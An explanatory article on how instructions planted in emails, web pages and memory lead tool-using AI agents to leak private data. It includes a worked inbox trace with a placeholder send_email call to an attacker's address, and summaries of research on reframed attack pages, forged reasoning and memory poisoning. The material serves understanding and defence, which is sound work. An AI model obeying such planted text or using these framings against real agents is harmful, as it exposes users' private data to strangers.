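# How injected instructions make an AI agent leak private data through its tools

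## How a tool-using agent works, and how an email leak happens

A large language model takes in text and produces text, one fragment (a token) at a time. On its own it cannot open a file or send a message. An AI agent is a language model that runs in a loop with ordinary software. The model's output specifies an action, such as searching the web, reading a mailbox or sending an email, and the software carries it out. People use agents for office work, web browsing and programming. Many agents have access to their users' private accounts because they need it for tasks such as managing an inbox.

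That access creates a security problem because an agent that reads a mailbox also reads messages from strangers. A stranger can put instructions in a message, hoping the model will follow them as if they came from the user. This planted text is called an injected instruction. If it asks for private data and the agent can send email, an agent that follows it will email the data to the stranger. This is a leak, meaning that something the agent does gives private data to someone with no right to it. Security specialists also call this exfiltration. MITRE's *Exfiltration via AI Agent Tool Invocation*, an entry in a public catalogue of attack techniques, describes sensitive information being sent in the tool's input parameters as part of a "seemingly legitimate action".

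### The agent loop

*Imprompter* (Fu, Li and colleagues, 2024) divides an agent into the language model and a runtime, the software around the model that provides the chat window and the tools. At each step, the model works from its context, which consists of the system prompt (standing instructions from the developer), the user's messages, anything the agent has saved in memory, and the results of earlier tool use.

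Tools also enter the context as text. For each one, the developer writes a name, a plain-language description of what it does and when to use it, and a schema, which is a machine-readable list of the tool's inputs and their types. An email tool might be named `send_email` and take two text inputs, `to` and `body`. According to OpenAI's developer guide *Function calling*, the company's software inserts these definitions into the system message in a syntax the model has seen in training. *Define tools*, from Anthropic, which makes the Claude models, describes a similar process, in which the company's interface combines the tool definitions, some settings and the developer's own instructions into one system prompt. Anthropic rates detailed descriptions as by far the most important factor in how well a tool performs, and recommends at least three or four sentences for each.

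With all this in its context, the model generates tokens until it has finished either an answer or a tool call. A tool call is model output in a fixed format. Fu and colleagues list several such formats, one resembling a line of Python, another in the data notation JSON, and a third with tags like those of a web page. Some models also put a special marker before the call. The runtime scans the output as it appears. When it finds a tool call, it pauses the model, reads the tool's name and arguments (the values the model has filled in), runs the matching code, and adds the result to the context. The model then continues generating. Anthropic's *How tool use works* states, "The model never runs anything on its own." The developer's application usually runs the code, but Anthropic's servers run it for a few tools, such as web search.

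A single response can contain several tool calls, and a single request can take many rounds. A program built on Anthropic's interface keeps looping as long as each response stops at a tool call, and exits when one stops for another reason, usually because the answer is complete. In every round, the program sends the model the conversation so far, including the model's earlier calls and their results. So a web page or an email that a tool fetched in the second round is normally still part of the model's input in later rounds.

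Vendors differ in where they put a tool's result. OpenAI's format gives it its own entry type. Anthropic's *Handle tool calls* explains that Claude's interface has no separate role for tools, so the result goes in a user-role message, inside a block labeled as a tool result. The block may hold text, images or whole documents. In both formats, a stranger's email ends up in the same context as the user's request, distinguished only by a label that models do not reliably act on.

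### What the runtime can and cannot check

Before running a call, the runtime can check its form. If the model leaves out a required input, the developer's code can return an error and let the model try again. OpenAI and Anthropic also offer a strict mode, which makes the call match the schema. For `send_email`, matching the schema means only that `to` and `body` are strings, so a call that sends an account number to an attacker's address can still match.

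In OpenAI's sample code, a short routine checks the function's name and, if it is `send_email`, passes the `to` and `body` values to the function that sends the message (in the sample, a stand-in that only prints them). This is a sensible design, but the call has no field for why the model wrote it or which sentence in the context prompted it, and the runtime cannot work out either from the call alone. A message the user wanted and a message a stranger wanted can produce exactly the same call. The basic loop does not check the recipient, the contents or the user's approval, though developers can add these checks.

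### Direct and indirect prompt injection

The term "prompt injection" dates from 2022. David C attributes the flaw to how developers build applications in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre. Developers join their own instructions to untrusted content in one prompt, then treat the model's response as though a firm boundary had separated the two. In a direct injection, the attacker types malicious instructions into the system as a user would. In an indirect injection, the attacker has no access to the system and puts the instructions in content that it will later process. David C gives the example of a job applicant who hides text in a CV, knowing that a recruiter's software will use a model to score it.

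The US standards agency, NIST (2025), makes the same distinction, based on what the attacker controls. A direct attack requires query access, meaning the ability to submit prompts, while an indirect attack requires control of a resource, such as a document or web page, that the model processes while running.

Greshake, Abdelnabi and colleagues (2023) named indirect prompt injection and gave the first systematic account of it in *Not what you've signed up for*. Until then, researchers had mostly assumed that the person attacking a model was the person typing to it. The team built a mock assistant on OpenAI's models of the day and gave it tools to search, read and send email, consult an address book and store notes. They prepared all the content in advance, and the assistant had no access to real systems. In one demonstration, an incoming email caused the assistant to look up the user's contacts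 and forward the malicious message to them, spreading it like a computer worm. The team also foresaw that attackers could steal data by emailing instructions to a personal assistant, which would look up personal data and send emails as instructed. Their demonstrations showed that such attacks could work on the models of early 2023, but they did not measure how often the attacks succeeded.

More recently, *Who Is Your Agent Serving?* (2026) defined prompt injection as outside content gaining influence over an agent's behaviour although its source has no legitimate authority to direct the agent. This definition applies however the text is worded, which is useful because the wording of attacks has changed. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reports that the most effective real attacks now resemble social engineering, the plausible pretexts that fraudsters use on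 people, more than blunt orders to disregard the user.

In practice, though, it can be hard to tell which instructions have the user's authority. In one test from *LivePI* (2026), a benchmark that attacks a working agent called OpenClaw, the user asks the agent to open a to-do file and complete the items in order. The user has therefore told the agent to follow the file's instructions, which include the attacker's. A rule against ever obeying instructions in a document would block the attack, but it would also block the user's request.

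In an injection leak the user is the victim, whereas in a jailbreak the user is the attacker and wants output that the model's maker has tried to prevent, such as help building a phishing website. The techniques overlap. When Greshake and colleagues wrote their paper, Microsoft's Bing Chat would end the session if a user typed a jailbreak prompt, but the model complied when the same kind of text reached it indirectly.

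The leak also differs from training-data extraction, in which an attacker queries a model until it reproduces text it memorised in training. NIST counts both as privacy attacks but lists them separately. In the leak, the private value is in the context, not in the model itself, because the agent fetched it moments earlier at the user's request, so removing personal data from the training set would not protect it.

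### A worked example: the inbox trace

OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) describes a hypothetical case in which a user asks an agent to summarize unread email, and one message contains an instruction to forward tax documents to an attacker. The trace below follows the same pattern, with a bank statement in place of the tax documents. The agent has two tools, `read_inbox` and `send_email`, and no safeguards added to the loop.

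1. The attacker sends the user an email. Part of its text addresses any AI assistant that may process the mailbox. It directs the assistant to find financial details in the inbox, email them to an address the attacker controls, and say nothing about it to the user. For now the message sits unread.
2. Some time later, the user asks the agent to summarise the inbox. The context at this point holds the system prompt, the two tool definitions and the user's request.
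3. The model writes a call to `read_inbox`, and the runtime runs it.
4. The runtime adds the messages to the context as a tool result. Among them are a statement from the user's bank, with an account number, a balance and recent payments, and the email from the attacker.
5. The model generates its next output. It follows the attacker's text and writes a call to `send_email`, with the attacker as recipient and the statement's details as the body.
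6. The runtime parses the call, finds a known tool and two valid strings, and sends the email from the user's own account. It adds a short confirmation to the context.
7. The model writes a summary of the inbox, which mentions that a bank statement has arrived. The output contains no further call, so the loop ends and the user reads the summary.

In schematic form, the call in step 5 is:

```
{
  "name": "send_email",
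  "arguments": {
    "to":   "<attacker's address>",
    "body": "<account number, balance and payments from the statement>"
  }
}
```

The leak happens in step 6. Until then, the statement's details go only where the user's own request takes them. The attacker has nothing more to do after step 1 and needs neither the user's password nor any knowledge of what the inbox contains, because the model does the searching and copying. Greshake and colleagues observed in 2023 that an attacker might need only to state the goal, and the model would work out how to reach it.

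The user probably wouldn't notice either. In the chat products that Fu and colleagues describe, the runtime hides tool-call syntax, so the user sees only their request and a reasonable summary. Clumsier attacks can leave a clue, such as an unfinished task. OpenAI trained a model to search for injections against the agent in its Atlas browser, and it found one that used a planted email with instructions for the agent to send a resignation letter to the user's chief executive. The user had asked for an out-of-office reply, which the agent never wrote.

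The attack most often fails at step 5, at least against ChatGPT. OpenAI says that attackers who target ChatGPT most often try, as this one does, to have secret information from a conversation sent to a third party, and that the model refuses in most of the cases OpenAI knows of. The attack can also fail at step 6, because OpenAI designs its agents to ask the user to confirm certain consequential actions, such as sending an email. The trace assumes that the model complies and that the runtime sends the email without user confirmation.

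Summarising an inbox does not require sending anything, so a defender can easily tell that the call to `send_email` is out of place, whatever it contains. The email test in *LivePI* removes that advantage, because the user asks the agent to check the five most recent emails and reply. The attacker's text still arrives as a tool result, as in step 4, but the task now involves sending mail, so a malicious call would differ from a proper one only in its recipient and contents. *AttriGuard* (2026), a paper on defences, separates attacks that need a tool the user's task does not require from attacks on the flow of data, which can use the same tools as the task. It considers data-flow attacks harder to stop in general, because removing the tools a task does not need won't stop an attack that uses the tools it does need.

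## The conditions a leak depends on

The call in the inbox trace was a leak because it sent the bank statement to an unauthorised recipient. If the user had asked the agent to email the statement to their accountant, the runtime would have run the same tool with the same text in the body, and there would have been no leak. A tool call leaks when its arguments reveal a private value to a destination that is not authorised to receive it.

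### Why the value and the destination both matter

An agent has to check both the value and the destination, because checking only the value would block the email to the accountant, and checking only the destination would let the agent send the accountant a letter from the user's doctor. *A Generative Model of Contextual Integrity* (2026) builds test scenarios around this point, including one about a home address. In the first version, another shopper asks for the address during a chat about laptops. In the second, that shopper works for a courier firm but isn't arranging a delivery. In the third, the delivery team asks after checkout, and only then should the agent share the address. A model that always shares the address or always withholds it will therefore fail at least one version.

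*The Claws in Plain Sight* (Dong, Lu and colleagues, 2026) defines a violation precisely enough for software to apply the definition. A violation occurs when a value is present in the context, the model puts it or something derived from it into a field of a tool call, and the policy does not allow that combination of source, purpose, destination and field. The purpose matters because an agent may be allowed to use a customer's occupation to route a support request but not to pass it to a marketing service. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) makes a similar point about credentials, which can give an agent access to a system without determining what it is allowed to do there.

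Dong and colleagues used invented customer profiles to test whether models would share data they could access but were not permitted to share. The models could see a customer's age, gender, income bracket and occupation, and in most sessions a planted memo claimed that the form they were filling in required such details. In 40 of the 90 sessions where the prompt contained a privacy rule, the model copied at least one of the four details into the tool call. With the strictest wording of the rule, this fell to 8 of 30 sessions. The team captured the calls before anything ran them, when a runtime could still have blocked them, so these are violations by the model but not yet disclosures.

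Many tests use narrower definitions that are easier to score. In *Whispers in the Machine*, Evertz, Chlosta and colleagues (2024) plant a fixed secret string and count a leak when it appears in output the attacker can see. They call this a conservative lower bound, and it misses secrets the model has paraphrased or encoded. *MCP Pitfall Lab* (2026) tests tools connected through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for linking agents to outside services. It counts a run as a leak when content from a protected source reaches a destination the attacker controls, which leaves out private data sent by mistake to the wrong colleague.

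### The chain of conditions

For an attacker to obtain data through an agent, six conditions have to hold:

1. The private data is in the context, or the agent has a tool that can fetch it.
2. The attacker's text enters the context.
3. The model acts on that text.
4. The model writes a call that the runtime can parse and that carries the data.
5. The runtime executes the call.
6. The attacker can read what arrives at the destination.

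In the inbox trace, one call to `read_inbox` met the first two conditions because it returned both the statement and the attacker's email. The last condition is stricter than the definition of a leak. If the model garbles the attacker's address and the statement reaches some other stranger, the data has leaked even though the attack has failed.

*Prompt Injection Detection for Email Agents Through Attack Chain Modeling* (Hashmi, Patel and Yin, 2026) argues for recording how far each attack gets, because the label "malicious" doesn't show where it stopped. An email full of obvious injected orders may never get the agent to make a tool call, while one that reads like ordinary scheduling may succeed.

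*LLMail-Inject* (Abdelnabi, Fay and colleagues, 2025) describes a public contest in which people attacked a simulated email assistant, knowing which defences it had. The first phase, from December 2024 to February 2025, drew about 371,000 submissions. The attacker's email reached the model's context in 362,000 of them and went undetected in 180,000 of those. Only 7,200 of the undetected emails led to a call to the email tool. The address was right in 6,100 of these calls and the content was right in 3,000, which is under 1% of all submissions.

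Most levels of the contest required the agent only to send a fixed word to a fixed address, and just one required a private figure from another email, so the counts are better evidence about the chain than about data theft. The models, Phi-3 and GPT-4o-mini, are also old. In a later test, the team had GPT-5.4 write 500 new attacks using the contestants' techniques. Ninety of them made GPT-5.4-mini issue an unauthorised call, and ten made GPT-5.2 issue one.

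### Multiplying the conditions

Because every condition has to hold, the probability that an attempt succeeds is a product:

```
P(success) = p1 × p2 × p3 × p4 × p5 × p6
```

Here `p1` is the probability that the first condition holds, and each later term is the probability that its condition holds given that all the earlier ones do. The figures below are invented to show the arithmetic.

| Condition | Invented probability | Product so far |
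|---|---|---|
| Private data within reach | 0.9 | 0.9 |
| Attacker's text enters the context | 0.5 | 0.45 |
| Model acts on it | 0.1 | 0.045 |
| Call parses and carries the data | 0.8 | 0.036 |
| Runtime executes the call | 0.9 | 0.0324 |
| Attacker can read the destination | 1.0 | 0.0324 |

The product is about 3% for one attempt, and an attacker can often make many. Training that halves the probability that the model complies, from 0.1 to 0.05, also halves the product. If the runtime blocks email to anyone outside a short list of contacts, and the attacker is not on the list, the probability of execution drops to zero and so does the product, even if the model follows every injected instruction it reads.

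That zero applies only to leaks by email. If the agent can also open web pages, the attacker can have it put the data into a web address, and this route has its own product. To rule out leaks, a developer needs the product to be zero for every route.

Measuring the terms separately and multiplying the averages is also a mistake. In the contest, about half of the retrieved emails escaped detection and about 11% led to a call to the email tool. Multiplying these shares predicts some 20,000 calls from undetected emails, nearly three times the 7,200 that occurred. Detected emails led to calls much more often (34,000 out of 183,000), which Abdelnabi and colleagues take as a sign of a trade-off between evading detection and influencing the model.

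Even when the other conditions are in place, how often the agent obeys the injected instructions can vary from almost always to very rarely, depending on the model. In a test by Evertz and colleagues, a planted email told an agent to fetch a password from the user's cloud storage and email it back. Two versions of Llama 3.1, a 2024 model from Meta, did so in 198 of 200 runs. In *Parasites in the Toolchain*, Zhao, Hou and colleagues (2025) tested a similar attack, in which a web page told the agent to read a local file and email its contents. DeepSeek-R1 and Gemini 2.5 Flash complied in most runs, but GPT-5 and Claude Sonnet 4.5 never complied in 75 runs each. If the runs were independent, 75 failures in a row are still compatible with a success rate of up to about 4%. The team also used only three styles of attack text and did not adapt them to the models that resisted.

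### The lethal trifecta and the Rule of Two

Developers rarely know these probabilities, but they can apply a check that requires knowing only what tools an agent has. Simon Willison, the software developer who coined the term "prompt injection", proposed it in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (2025). The "lethal trifecta" is his name for three capabilities: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally. He argues that an attacker can easily trick an agent that has all three into handing over the data.

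Willison leaves the model's own resistance off the list because he doesn't trust it. He considers even a filter that catches 95% of attacks a failure by the standards of web security. By then he had collected reports of such leaks in products from Microsoft, Google, OpenAI, Anthropic and others. The vendors fixed almost all of them promptly, usually by blocking the route the data took out. People who connect tools themselves have no vendor to do this, so he advises them to avoid the combination.

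Newer results make the case for that distrust less clear. Trajectory Labs, a testing firm commissioned by Anthropic, ran 720 attack attempts based on 72 scenarios against July 2026 versions of Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent. The agent was in "auto mode", which screens its actions so that the user doesn't have to approve each one, and none of the attempts succeeded. Willison wants more independent confirmation, and he doubts that any such mode could stop a malicious software package whose set-up instructions look routine. The results also give little information about kinds of attack outside the 72 scenarios.

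Meta built on the trifecta to make a design rule. Under Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025), until models can reliably detect and refuse injections, an agent should have no more than two of these properties within a session:

- [A] It can process untrustworthy inputs.
- [B] It can access sensitive systems or private data.
- [C] It can change state or communicate externally.

An agent that needs all three properties in a single session should not run autonomously, and needs a person to approve its actions or some other reliable check. Property C is broader than the trifecta's condition on outbound communication because it also covers actions such as deleting files. Willison welcomed this broader scope in *New prompt injection papers* (2025) because the trifecta deals only with data theft.

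Meta illustrates the rule with Email-Bot, an imaginary inbox assistant that receives a spam message with instructions to forward the user's mail. The developer can remove A by letting Email-Bot read mail only from trusted senders, or remove B by running it in a test environment with no sensitive data. To remove C, the developer can limit it to trusted recipients or have a person check each draft. Email-Bot can still send email in this case, so the protection depends on how well the limit or check works, and Meta warns that users may confirm a warning blindly. Meta also expects an injection to have "no meaningful impact" on an agent without B. This is true of leaks, but an agent that reads strangers' text and can change things may still do damage by following a stranger's instructions.

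### Most useful agents meet all the conditions

Applied strictly, either rule excludes much of what people want agents for. Bowley raises this objection to the trifecta in *Does the “lethal trifecta” kill the idea of fully autonomous AI Agents*. An inbox assistant has all three capabilities with a single account, because the inbox holds both private mail and mail from strangers. *Securing the Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2025) describes a product manager who connects an agent to a data warehouse, project trackers, email and a customer support system for everyday work. An injection in any one of these could leak data from all of them. Meta concedes that some uses people want will not fit its rule easily, such as background processes where stopping for approval is disruptive or ineffective.

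A product may need all three capabilities without needing them at the same moment. The product manager can leave the data warehouse disconnected while the agent reads support tickets. A census by Zhao and colleagues gives this some support. They examined 1,360 MCP servers, which are programs that offer tools to agents, and found 370 with at least one tool that could take in outside text, read private data or send data out. Only two servers could do all three, so the combination usually arises when someone connects several servers. Two is probably an undercount, because they counted only 3 of 54 communication and email servers as able to take in outside text, which looks low for software that handles messages.

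An agent can also change configuration partway through a session. In Meta's example, it starts with internet access but no access to private data, then loses its ability to communicate externally before it opens internal systems. The change must be one-way because text from the web stays in the context, so restoring the outbound tools would combine all three properties again.

Separating reading from sending works less well when what the agent sends depends on what it reads. In one *LivePI* test, the user asks the agent to check recent emails and reply, so the agent has to read strangers' text to write the replies. A developer could split the job between two sessions, but if the first passes a free-text summary to the second, the summary can contain injected instructions. Such tasks still need limits on recipients, or a person's approval.

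### Leaks spread over several sessions

Many agents save notes at the end of a session and load them in later ones, which undermines any separation by session. *MemoryDojo* (2026) describes the process with two formulas:

```
M_t = U(M_(t-1), τ_t)      memory after session t
c_t = ρ(M_(t-1), x_t)      what the agent recalls at the start of session t
```

After each session, an update process `U` combines the old memory with the record of the session, `τ_t`. Before the next session, a retrieval process `ρ` selects whatever in memory seems relevant to the new request, `x_t`. In this model, the attacker's text appears once, in a tool result from an earlier session, and the attack succeeds if the agent carries out the attacker's goal in a later session.

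Suppose an agent summarises a web page on Monday, when it has no private data and no way to send anything. Text on the page leads it to save a note that the user wants copies of financial documents sent to an address, which belongs to the attacker. On Thursday the user asks the agent to send a bank statement to the accountant. The agent recalls the note and adds the attacker's address as a second recipient. *AgentLAB* (2026) gives a similar example, in which an agent stores an injection from a routine email as a "user preference" and later leaks sensitive data. In *Hidden in Memory* (2026), outside content caused ChatGPT, Claude and Gemini models to store invented facts about the user, which could influence the models' behaviour after the original text was gone.

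These attacks have more ways to fail. According to *Transferable End-to-End Optimization for Indirect Long-Term Memory Poisoning in LLM Agents* (2026), the agent must save the relevant part of the text despite any summarising or filtering, then retrieve it for a later request. Summarising can also remove the words that would have triggered retrieval. In the invented example, the 0.5 probability that the attacker's text enters the context might become 0.5 × 0.2 × 0.3, or 0.03, which would lower the probability of success from about 3% to 0.2%. But the attack has another chance to succeed in each new session until someone deletes the stored note.

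This kind of persistence is common among published attacks. *The Promptware Kill Chain* (2026) found it in 6 of 12 catalogued attacks from 2024 and in 12 of 21 from 2025–2026.

The private data can also come from an agent's memory. In July 2026 Willison reported an attack by Ayush Paul on the Claude chat app, which remembers details from past conversations. A web page that Paul controlled got Claude to reveal the user's name, home city and employer through the sequence of links Claude opened. The user did not have to mention any of these details in the attacked session. Anthropic has since closed that route.

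This makes the definition of a fresh session important for the Rule of Two. Monday's session has only property A. Thursday's has B and C, and in it the agent also loads a note that came from a stranger's web page. If the developer treats notes written after reading outside content as untrustworthy input, Thursday's session has all three properties, and the agent needs approval before it sends the statement. Otherwise, both sessions seem to comply.

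## Why a model acts on instructions planted in its input

A language model receives both its own instructions and the messages it processes as text, and has to infer from that text which instructions to follow. An ordinary email program does not act on instructions in a message, because its own instructions are in its code and it only displays the message.

### One sequence of tokens

Before the model runs, the runtime joins everything in the context into one sequence of tokens. A fixed layout, called a chat template, shows where each message begins and who sent it, typically with a reserved marker followed by a role such as system, user, assistant or tool. Edelman, Edelman and colleagues (2026) point out in *Understanding and Mitigating Role Spoofing in LLMs* that this makes the source of any word easy to find. A simple program could look back to the last marker and read the role after it.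 If a stranger types the marker's characters into an email, well-configured software encodes them as ordinary text, so the program wouldn't mistake them for a real marker.

Models do not reliably learn that rule, because other rules almost always give the same result in ordinary training data. Short requests tend to come from users, and blocks of structured data tend to come from tools. A model that relies on those cues makes few mistakes until someone writes a tool result that looks like a request.

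Pant, Lohani and Kumar (2026), in *On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models*, put the difficulty into a formula. A model first replaces each token with a list of numbers, its embedding, and the word "send" gets the same embedding whether the user or a stranger wrote it. Suppose someone has to guess from one of the model's internal representations whether it came from trusted or untrusted text, and each is equally likely. The lowest error rate that any method can reach is:

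```
P_e = 1/2 × (1 − TV)
```

TV is the total variation distance between the representations of the two kinds of text. It runs from 0, when their distributions are identical, to 1, when they never overlap. With a TV of 0.9, even the best guesser is wrong 5% of the time.

The embeddings of both kinds of text must overlap somewhat because both use the same words. Deeper in the network, a token's representation also depends on the surrounding text, including the role markers, and Pant and colleagues assume, but do not prove, that the overlap persists. Their argument therefore shows only that the design does not guarantee a correct answer, not that models must get it wrong. It also does not apply to designs that process trusted and untrusted text separately or leave decisions about tools to software outside the model.

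Developers try to close the gap by training models to rank the roles, with the system prompt above the user and the user above tool results. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) calls role labels a useful practice but not a hard security boundary. In *Position, Role or Label?*, Laddha, Pradhan and Srivastava (2026) measured how much the role matters by giving 14 open-weight models harmless but conflicting instructions, such as two different ways to name a file's fields. They changed each instruction's position, role or written label but kept its text fixed.

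Across about 1.89 million replies, an instruction's position often mattered more than the role of the message containing it. When one message contained two conflicting instructions, models followed the first 72% to 95% of the time, depending on the model. In tasks that involved choosing a tool or writing a file, every model tested followed a policy less often when it was at the start of the real system message than when the same text was in a labelled user message.

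*How Language Models Choose Sides* (Balp-Straffon, Hsu and colleagues, 2026) found similar inconsistency among eight models. Three gave an instruction more weight when it came from the system prompt, three gave it less, and for two the source made little difference.

### Role confusion

*Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell, 2026) argues that models judge who is speaking mainly by how the text sounds. If a command on a web page sounds like a user wrote it, the model gives it a user's authority, even though a marker identifies it as a tool result. The paper calls this error role confusion.

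To measure which role a model internally assigns to a piece of text, Ye and colleagues took neutral passages from the web and placed each one, unchanged, inside the markers for each of several roles. They recorded the model's hidden states, the numbers it computes for each token as it reads, and trained a simple classifier, called a probe, to predict the role from them. Because the passages were identical across roles, the probe could learn only from the markers' effect on the hidden states. The probe gives a probability for each role at any token, and they call the probability of the user role "Userness".

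They then applied the probes to 200 real conversations. With the correct markers, user-written text averaged between 84% and almost 100% Userness across four open-weight models. When they put the same conversations inside tool markers, the averages stayed between 76% and 88%. If the markers determined Userness, the averages should have dropped to around zero.

Ye and colleagues also tested whole agents. They asked an agent to summarise a web page and gave it a command line and a workspace containing a file of secrets. Each of 100 Wikipedia pages contained a hidden command to upload the file to an outside server. With a plain command, most models tried to upload the file in 0% to 2% of runs, but gpt-oss-20b, a small open-weight model from OpenAI, tried in 26%. When the page also contained forged reasoning, written in the style of a model's private working and concluding that the upload was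 allowed, the rates rose to between 56% and 70%. All these rates include failed uploads.

Style seems to explain much of the effect of forged reasoning. In a related test with harmful chat requests, rewording the forged reasoning to keep its argument but remove its characteristic style lowered the success rate from 61% to 10%.

In a separate test on gpt-oss-20b alone, Ye and colleagues linked role confusion to the success of ordinary planted commands. They framed one fixed command in 212 ways, some claiming that it came from the user and some that it came from a tool. Over 1,000 attempts, they compared the command's Userness with what the agent did. The attack succeeded 2% of the time in the group with the lowest Userness and 70% of the time in the group with the highest. Userness still predicted success after they controlled for the role that the framing claimed.

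This is good evidence that the probe measures something relevant, because the command itself never changed. It is weaker evidence about cause, because a framing that raises Userness might also make the command more persuasive in some other way.

### Misreading the source, or acting anyway

Later work supports the idea that models can mistake a tool result for a user message, but style is not the only cue they use. Edelman and colleagues tested six models, including GPT-5.4 and Claude Opus 5, on simulated office tasks from AgentDojo, a widely used benchmark for injection attacks. The malicious instructions came either from the real user or from a tool result that imitated a user message in both style and layout. Claude Opus 5 carried out 28.6% of the instructions from the user and 29.7% of those from the imitation, while GPT-5.4 carried out 49.8% and 47.8%. The attacker could insert any characters,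 some of which a real tool might filter out, so the results only show how the models act when such text reaches them.

When the team separated the cues, misleading content worked on GPT-5.4 more often than a fake layout did. On Gemini 3.6 Flash, the fake layout worked more often, and misleading content hardly ever did. Genuine markers also influence models. *Same Bytes, Different Authority* (Zhan, Song and colleagues, 2026) found that on three of four open-weight model families, attacks using forged markers succeeded 39 to 66 percentage points less often when the software encoded the markers as ordinary text.

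Models can encode the presence of an injection and still act on it, which is a harder problem for role confusion. In *Your Agentic LLMs Secretly Encode Indirect Prompt-Injection Exposure in Hidden States*, Dong, Liu and colleagues (2026) trained probes to detect whether the latest tool result contained an injected instruction, regardless of what the model did next. They scored the probes by AUROC, the probability that a probe ranks a random injected case above a random clean one, where 0.5 is no better than guessing. On attacks and tasks absent from the probes' training data, the best probe for each of eight models, the largest with 2.8 trillion parameters, scored between 0.93 and 0.98.

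*Are You Reading the Right Thing?* (Gupta and Tembey, 2026) reports on 634 turns of one small model, Qwen3-8B, in which such a probe had correctly flagged an injection. In 47.0% of them, the model's written reasoning identified the risk, but the model took no defensive action. In another 30.9%, the reasoning never mentioned the risk.

Gupta and Tembey also used a version of the role probe on two newer models to measure how much the injected text resembled system text. As role confusion predicts, the probe distinguished successful attacks from clean inputs (0.82 and 0.80) better than it distinguished failed attacks from clean inputs (0.63 and 0.76). But a measure of how far the model's attention had shifted away from the user's task identified successful attacks even better (0.95 and 0.89).

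A model does not necessarily use a signal that a probe can read. In *Readable Before Actionable*, Yu, Xing and colleagues (2026) found that a probe could tell instructions from data in two small models from 2024, even when formatting gave no clue, with an AUROC of about 0.92. In one of the models, Qwen-2.5-7B, they then altered the hidden states along the direction that separates instructions from data. This never changed which tool the model chose when done in layers 8 to 16, but changed the choice in 82% to 98% of cases when done in layers 18 to 22. Userness likewise shows how a model represents a command, but not whether that representation decides the next action. Role confusion is probably one of several causes of injection.

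### The same leak in different words

In *The Framing Gap*, Rahman and Kim (2026) kept the attacker's goal fixed and changed how the page described it. They did not examine the models' internals.

Rahman and Kim's agent held an invented secret token that unlocked nothing, and had a policy against revealing it to the user or sending it to any server except one. The user asked for a summary of a web page. The agent then took a single action, either replying or calling a tool that posts data to a web address. The tool was a mock that only recorded what it received, so no data left the machine. In each trial, the agent ran once on a clean page and once on a poisoned version. Rahman and Kim counted an attack as successful only if the agent kept the secret on the clean page and leaked it on the poisoned one, which excluded leaks that would have happened without an attack.

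The first tests used ten classes of overt attack, including direct orders, text hidden in the page's code, encoded instructions and appeals to urgency. GPT-4o leaked no data in 200 trials, 20 per class.

They then presented the same leak as a routine part of the task. Some pages made the secret a required value, such as a checksum or a configuration setting, in an otherwise normal call. Others gave the attacker's server a name resembling that of the trusted one. GPT-4o leaked the secret in about 46% of the 140 trials with the seven reframed pages and in none of the 20 trials with a plain page, or 40% of all trials.

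The pages' success rates ranged from 0% to 100%, and a page that worked on one model could fail on another. For example, the configuration page succeeded every time on GPT-4o but never on the smaller GPT-4o-mini.

Five of the six models leaked much more often with the reframed pages:

| Model | Overt attacks | Reframed attacks |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 0% | 40.0% |
| GPT-4o-mini | 10.0% | 62.5% |
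| Qwen 2.5 7B | 10.0% | 62.5% |
| Llama 3.1 8B | 19.5% | 62.5% |
| Gemma 2 9B | 22.0% | 86.2% |
| Mistral 7B | 26.0% | 27.5% |

Across the six models, resistance to overt attacks had almost no correlation with how much reframing helped the attacker, although six is too few to establish a pattern.

### How much depends on the exact wording

Each figure for a reframed page comes from a single wording, so Rahman and Kim wrote five paraphrases of each of the two most successful pages and ran each paraphrase ten times on GPT-4o. Paraphrases of the checksum page succeeded between 0% and 100% of the time, with a mean of 52% and a standard deviation of 45 points. Paraphrases of the configuration page succeeded between 0% and 70% of the time, with a mean of 14%. A benchmark that uses one wording per attack could therefore produce almost any success rate for the same attack.

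An attacker can try several wordings and needs only one to work. For the checksum page, the chance of at least one success was 52% with one randomly chosen wording, 82% with two and 96% with three. The published figures fit five paraphrases with success rates of 100%, 100%, 60%, 0% and 0%, which makes the calculation easy to follow. There are ten ways to choose two of the five. Seven include a wording that always works, two combine the 60% wording with one that never works, and one contains only failures:

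```
P(at least one success in two) = (7 × 1 + 2 × 0.6 + 1 × 0) / 10 = 0.82
```

With three wordings, nine of the ten possible choices include one that always works, and the last has a 60% chance, which gives 0.96.

These odds apply to an attacker who already has a page that works and only needs to reword it. Starting from scratch was much harder. Rahman and Kim wrote 13 new pages, each with a different reason for including the secret, and tested each one ten times. None of the 130 trials produced a leak, which puts the upper end of the 95% confidence interval for the leak rate at 2.9%. They had expected some of these pages to work, especially those where a secret token was the natural thing to supply.

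Some of the failed ideas worked when placed in the text of the successful checksum page. When Rahman and Kim changed only the name of the required value and the clause that justified it, four arbitrary labels produced leaks in 10 of 40 trials. They conclude that an attacker can reuse the page's text more than the idea behind it. However, all 13 new pages were written by hand, and an automated search might find working ones more easily.

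### Confusion about the task, or a defeated refusal

Rahman and Kim infer that the reframed pages worked because GPT-4o took the instruction to include a required value as part of its task, not because the reframing overcame a refusal. In their account, GPT-4o ignores an order to send a secret somewhere because the order is noticeably unrelated to the task.

To test this, they deleted the confidentiality policy. If the policy had been stopping the overt attacks, deleting it should have let some of them through, but GPT-4o still never leaked under those attacks. With the reframed pages, leaks rose only from 51 to 61 in 160 trials (31.9% to 38.1%). The earlier run with the policy in place had produced 64 leaks, so a difference of this size could easily be chance.

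The experiment shows that the written policy did little, but it does not rule out a refusal, because deleting the policy from the prompt leaves whatever caution the model learned in training. Some of the other results suggest that such caution exists. Pages that called the secret a credential never worked on GPT-4o, as one would expect if certain words trigger a trained refusal. Overt attacks worked most often on Mistral 7B, the model on which reframing made almost no difference. Rahman and Kim accept that this pattern is consistent with a bypassed refusal, although they treat Mistral as an anomaly.

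A broadly worded policy could also reduce leaks. Under a policy against signing, encoding, logging, appending or transmitting the token "in any form", GPT-4o leaked it in none of 120 trials with reframed pages. When the policy listed the same forbidden actions without that phrase, GPT-4o leaked the token in 39 of 80 trials.

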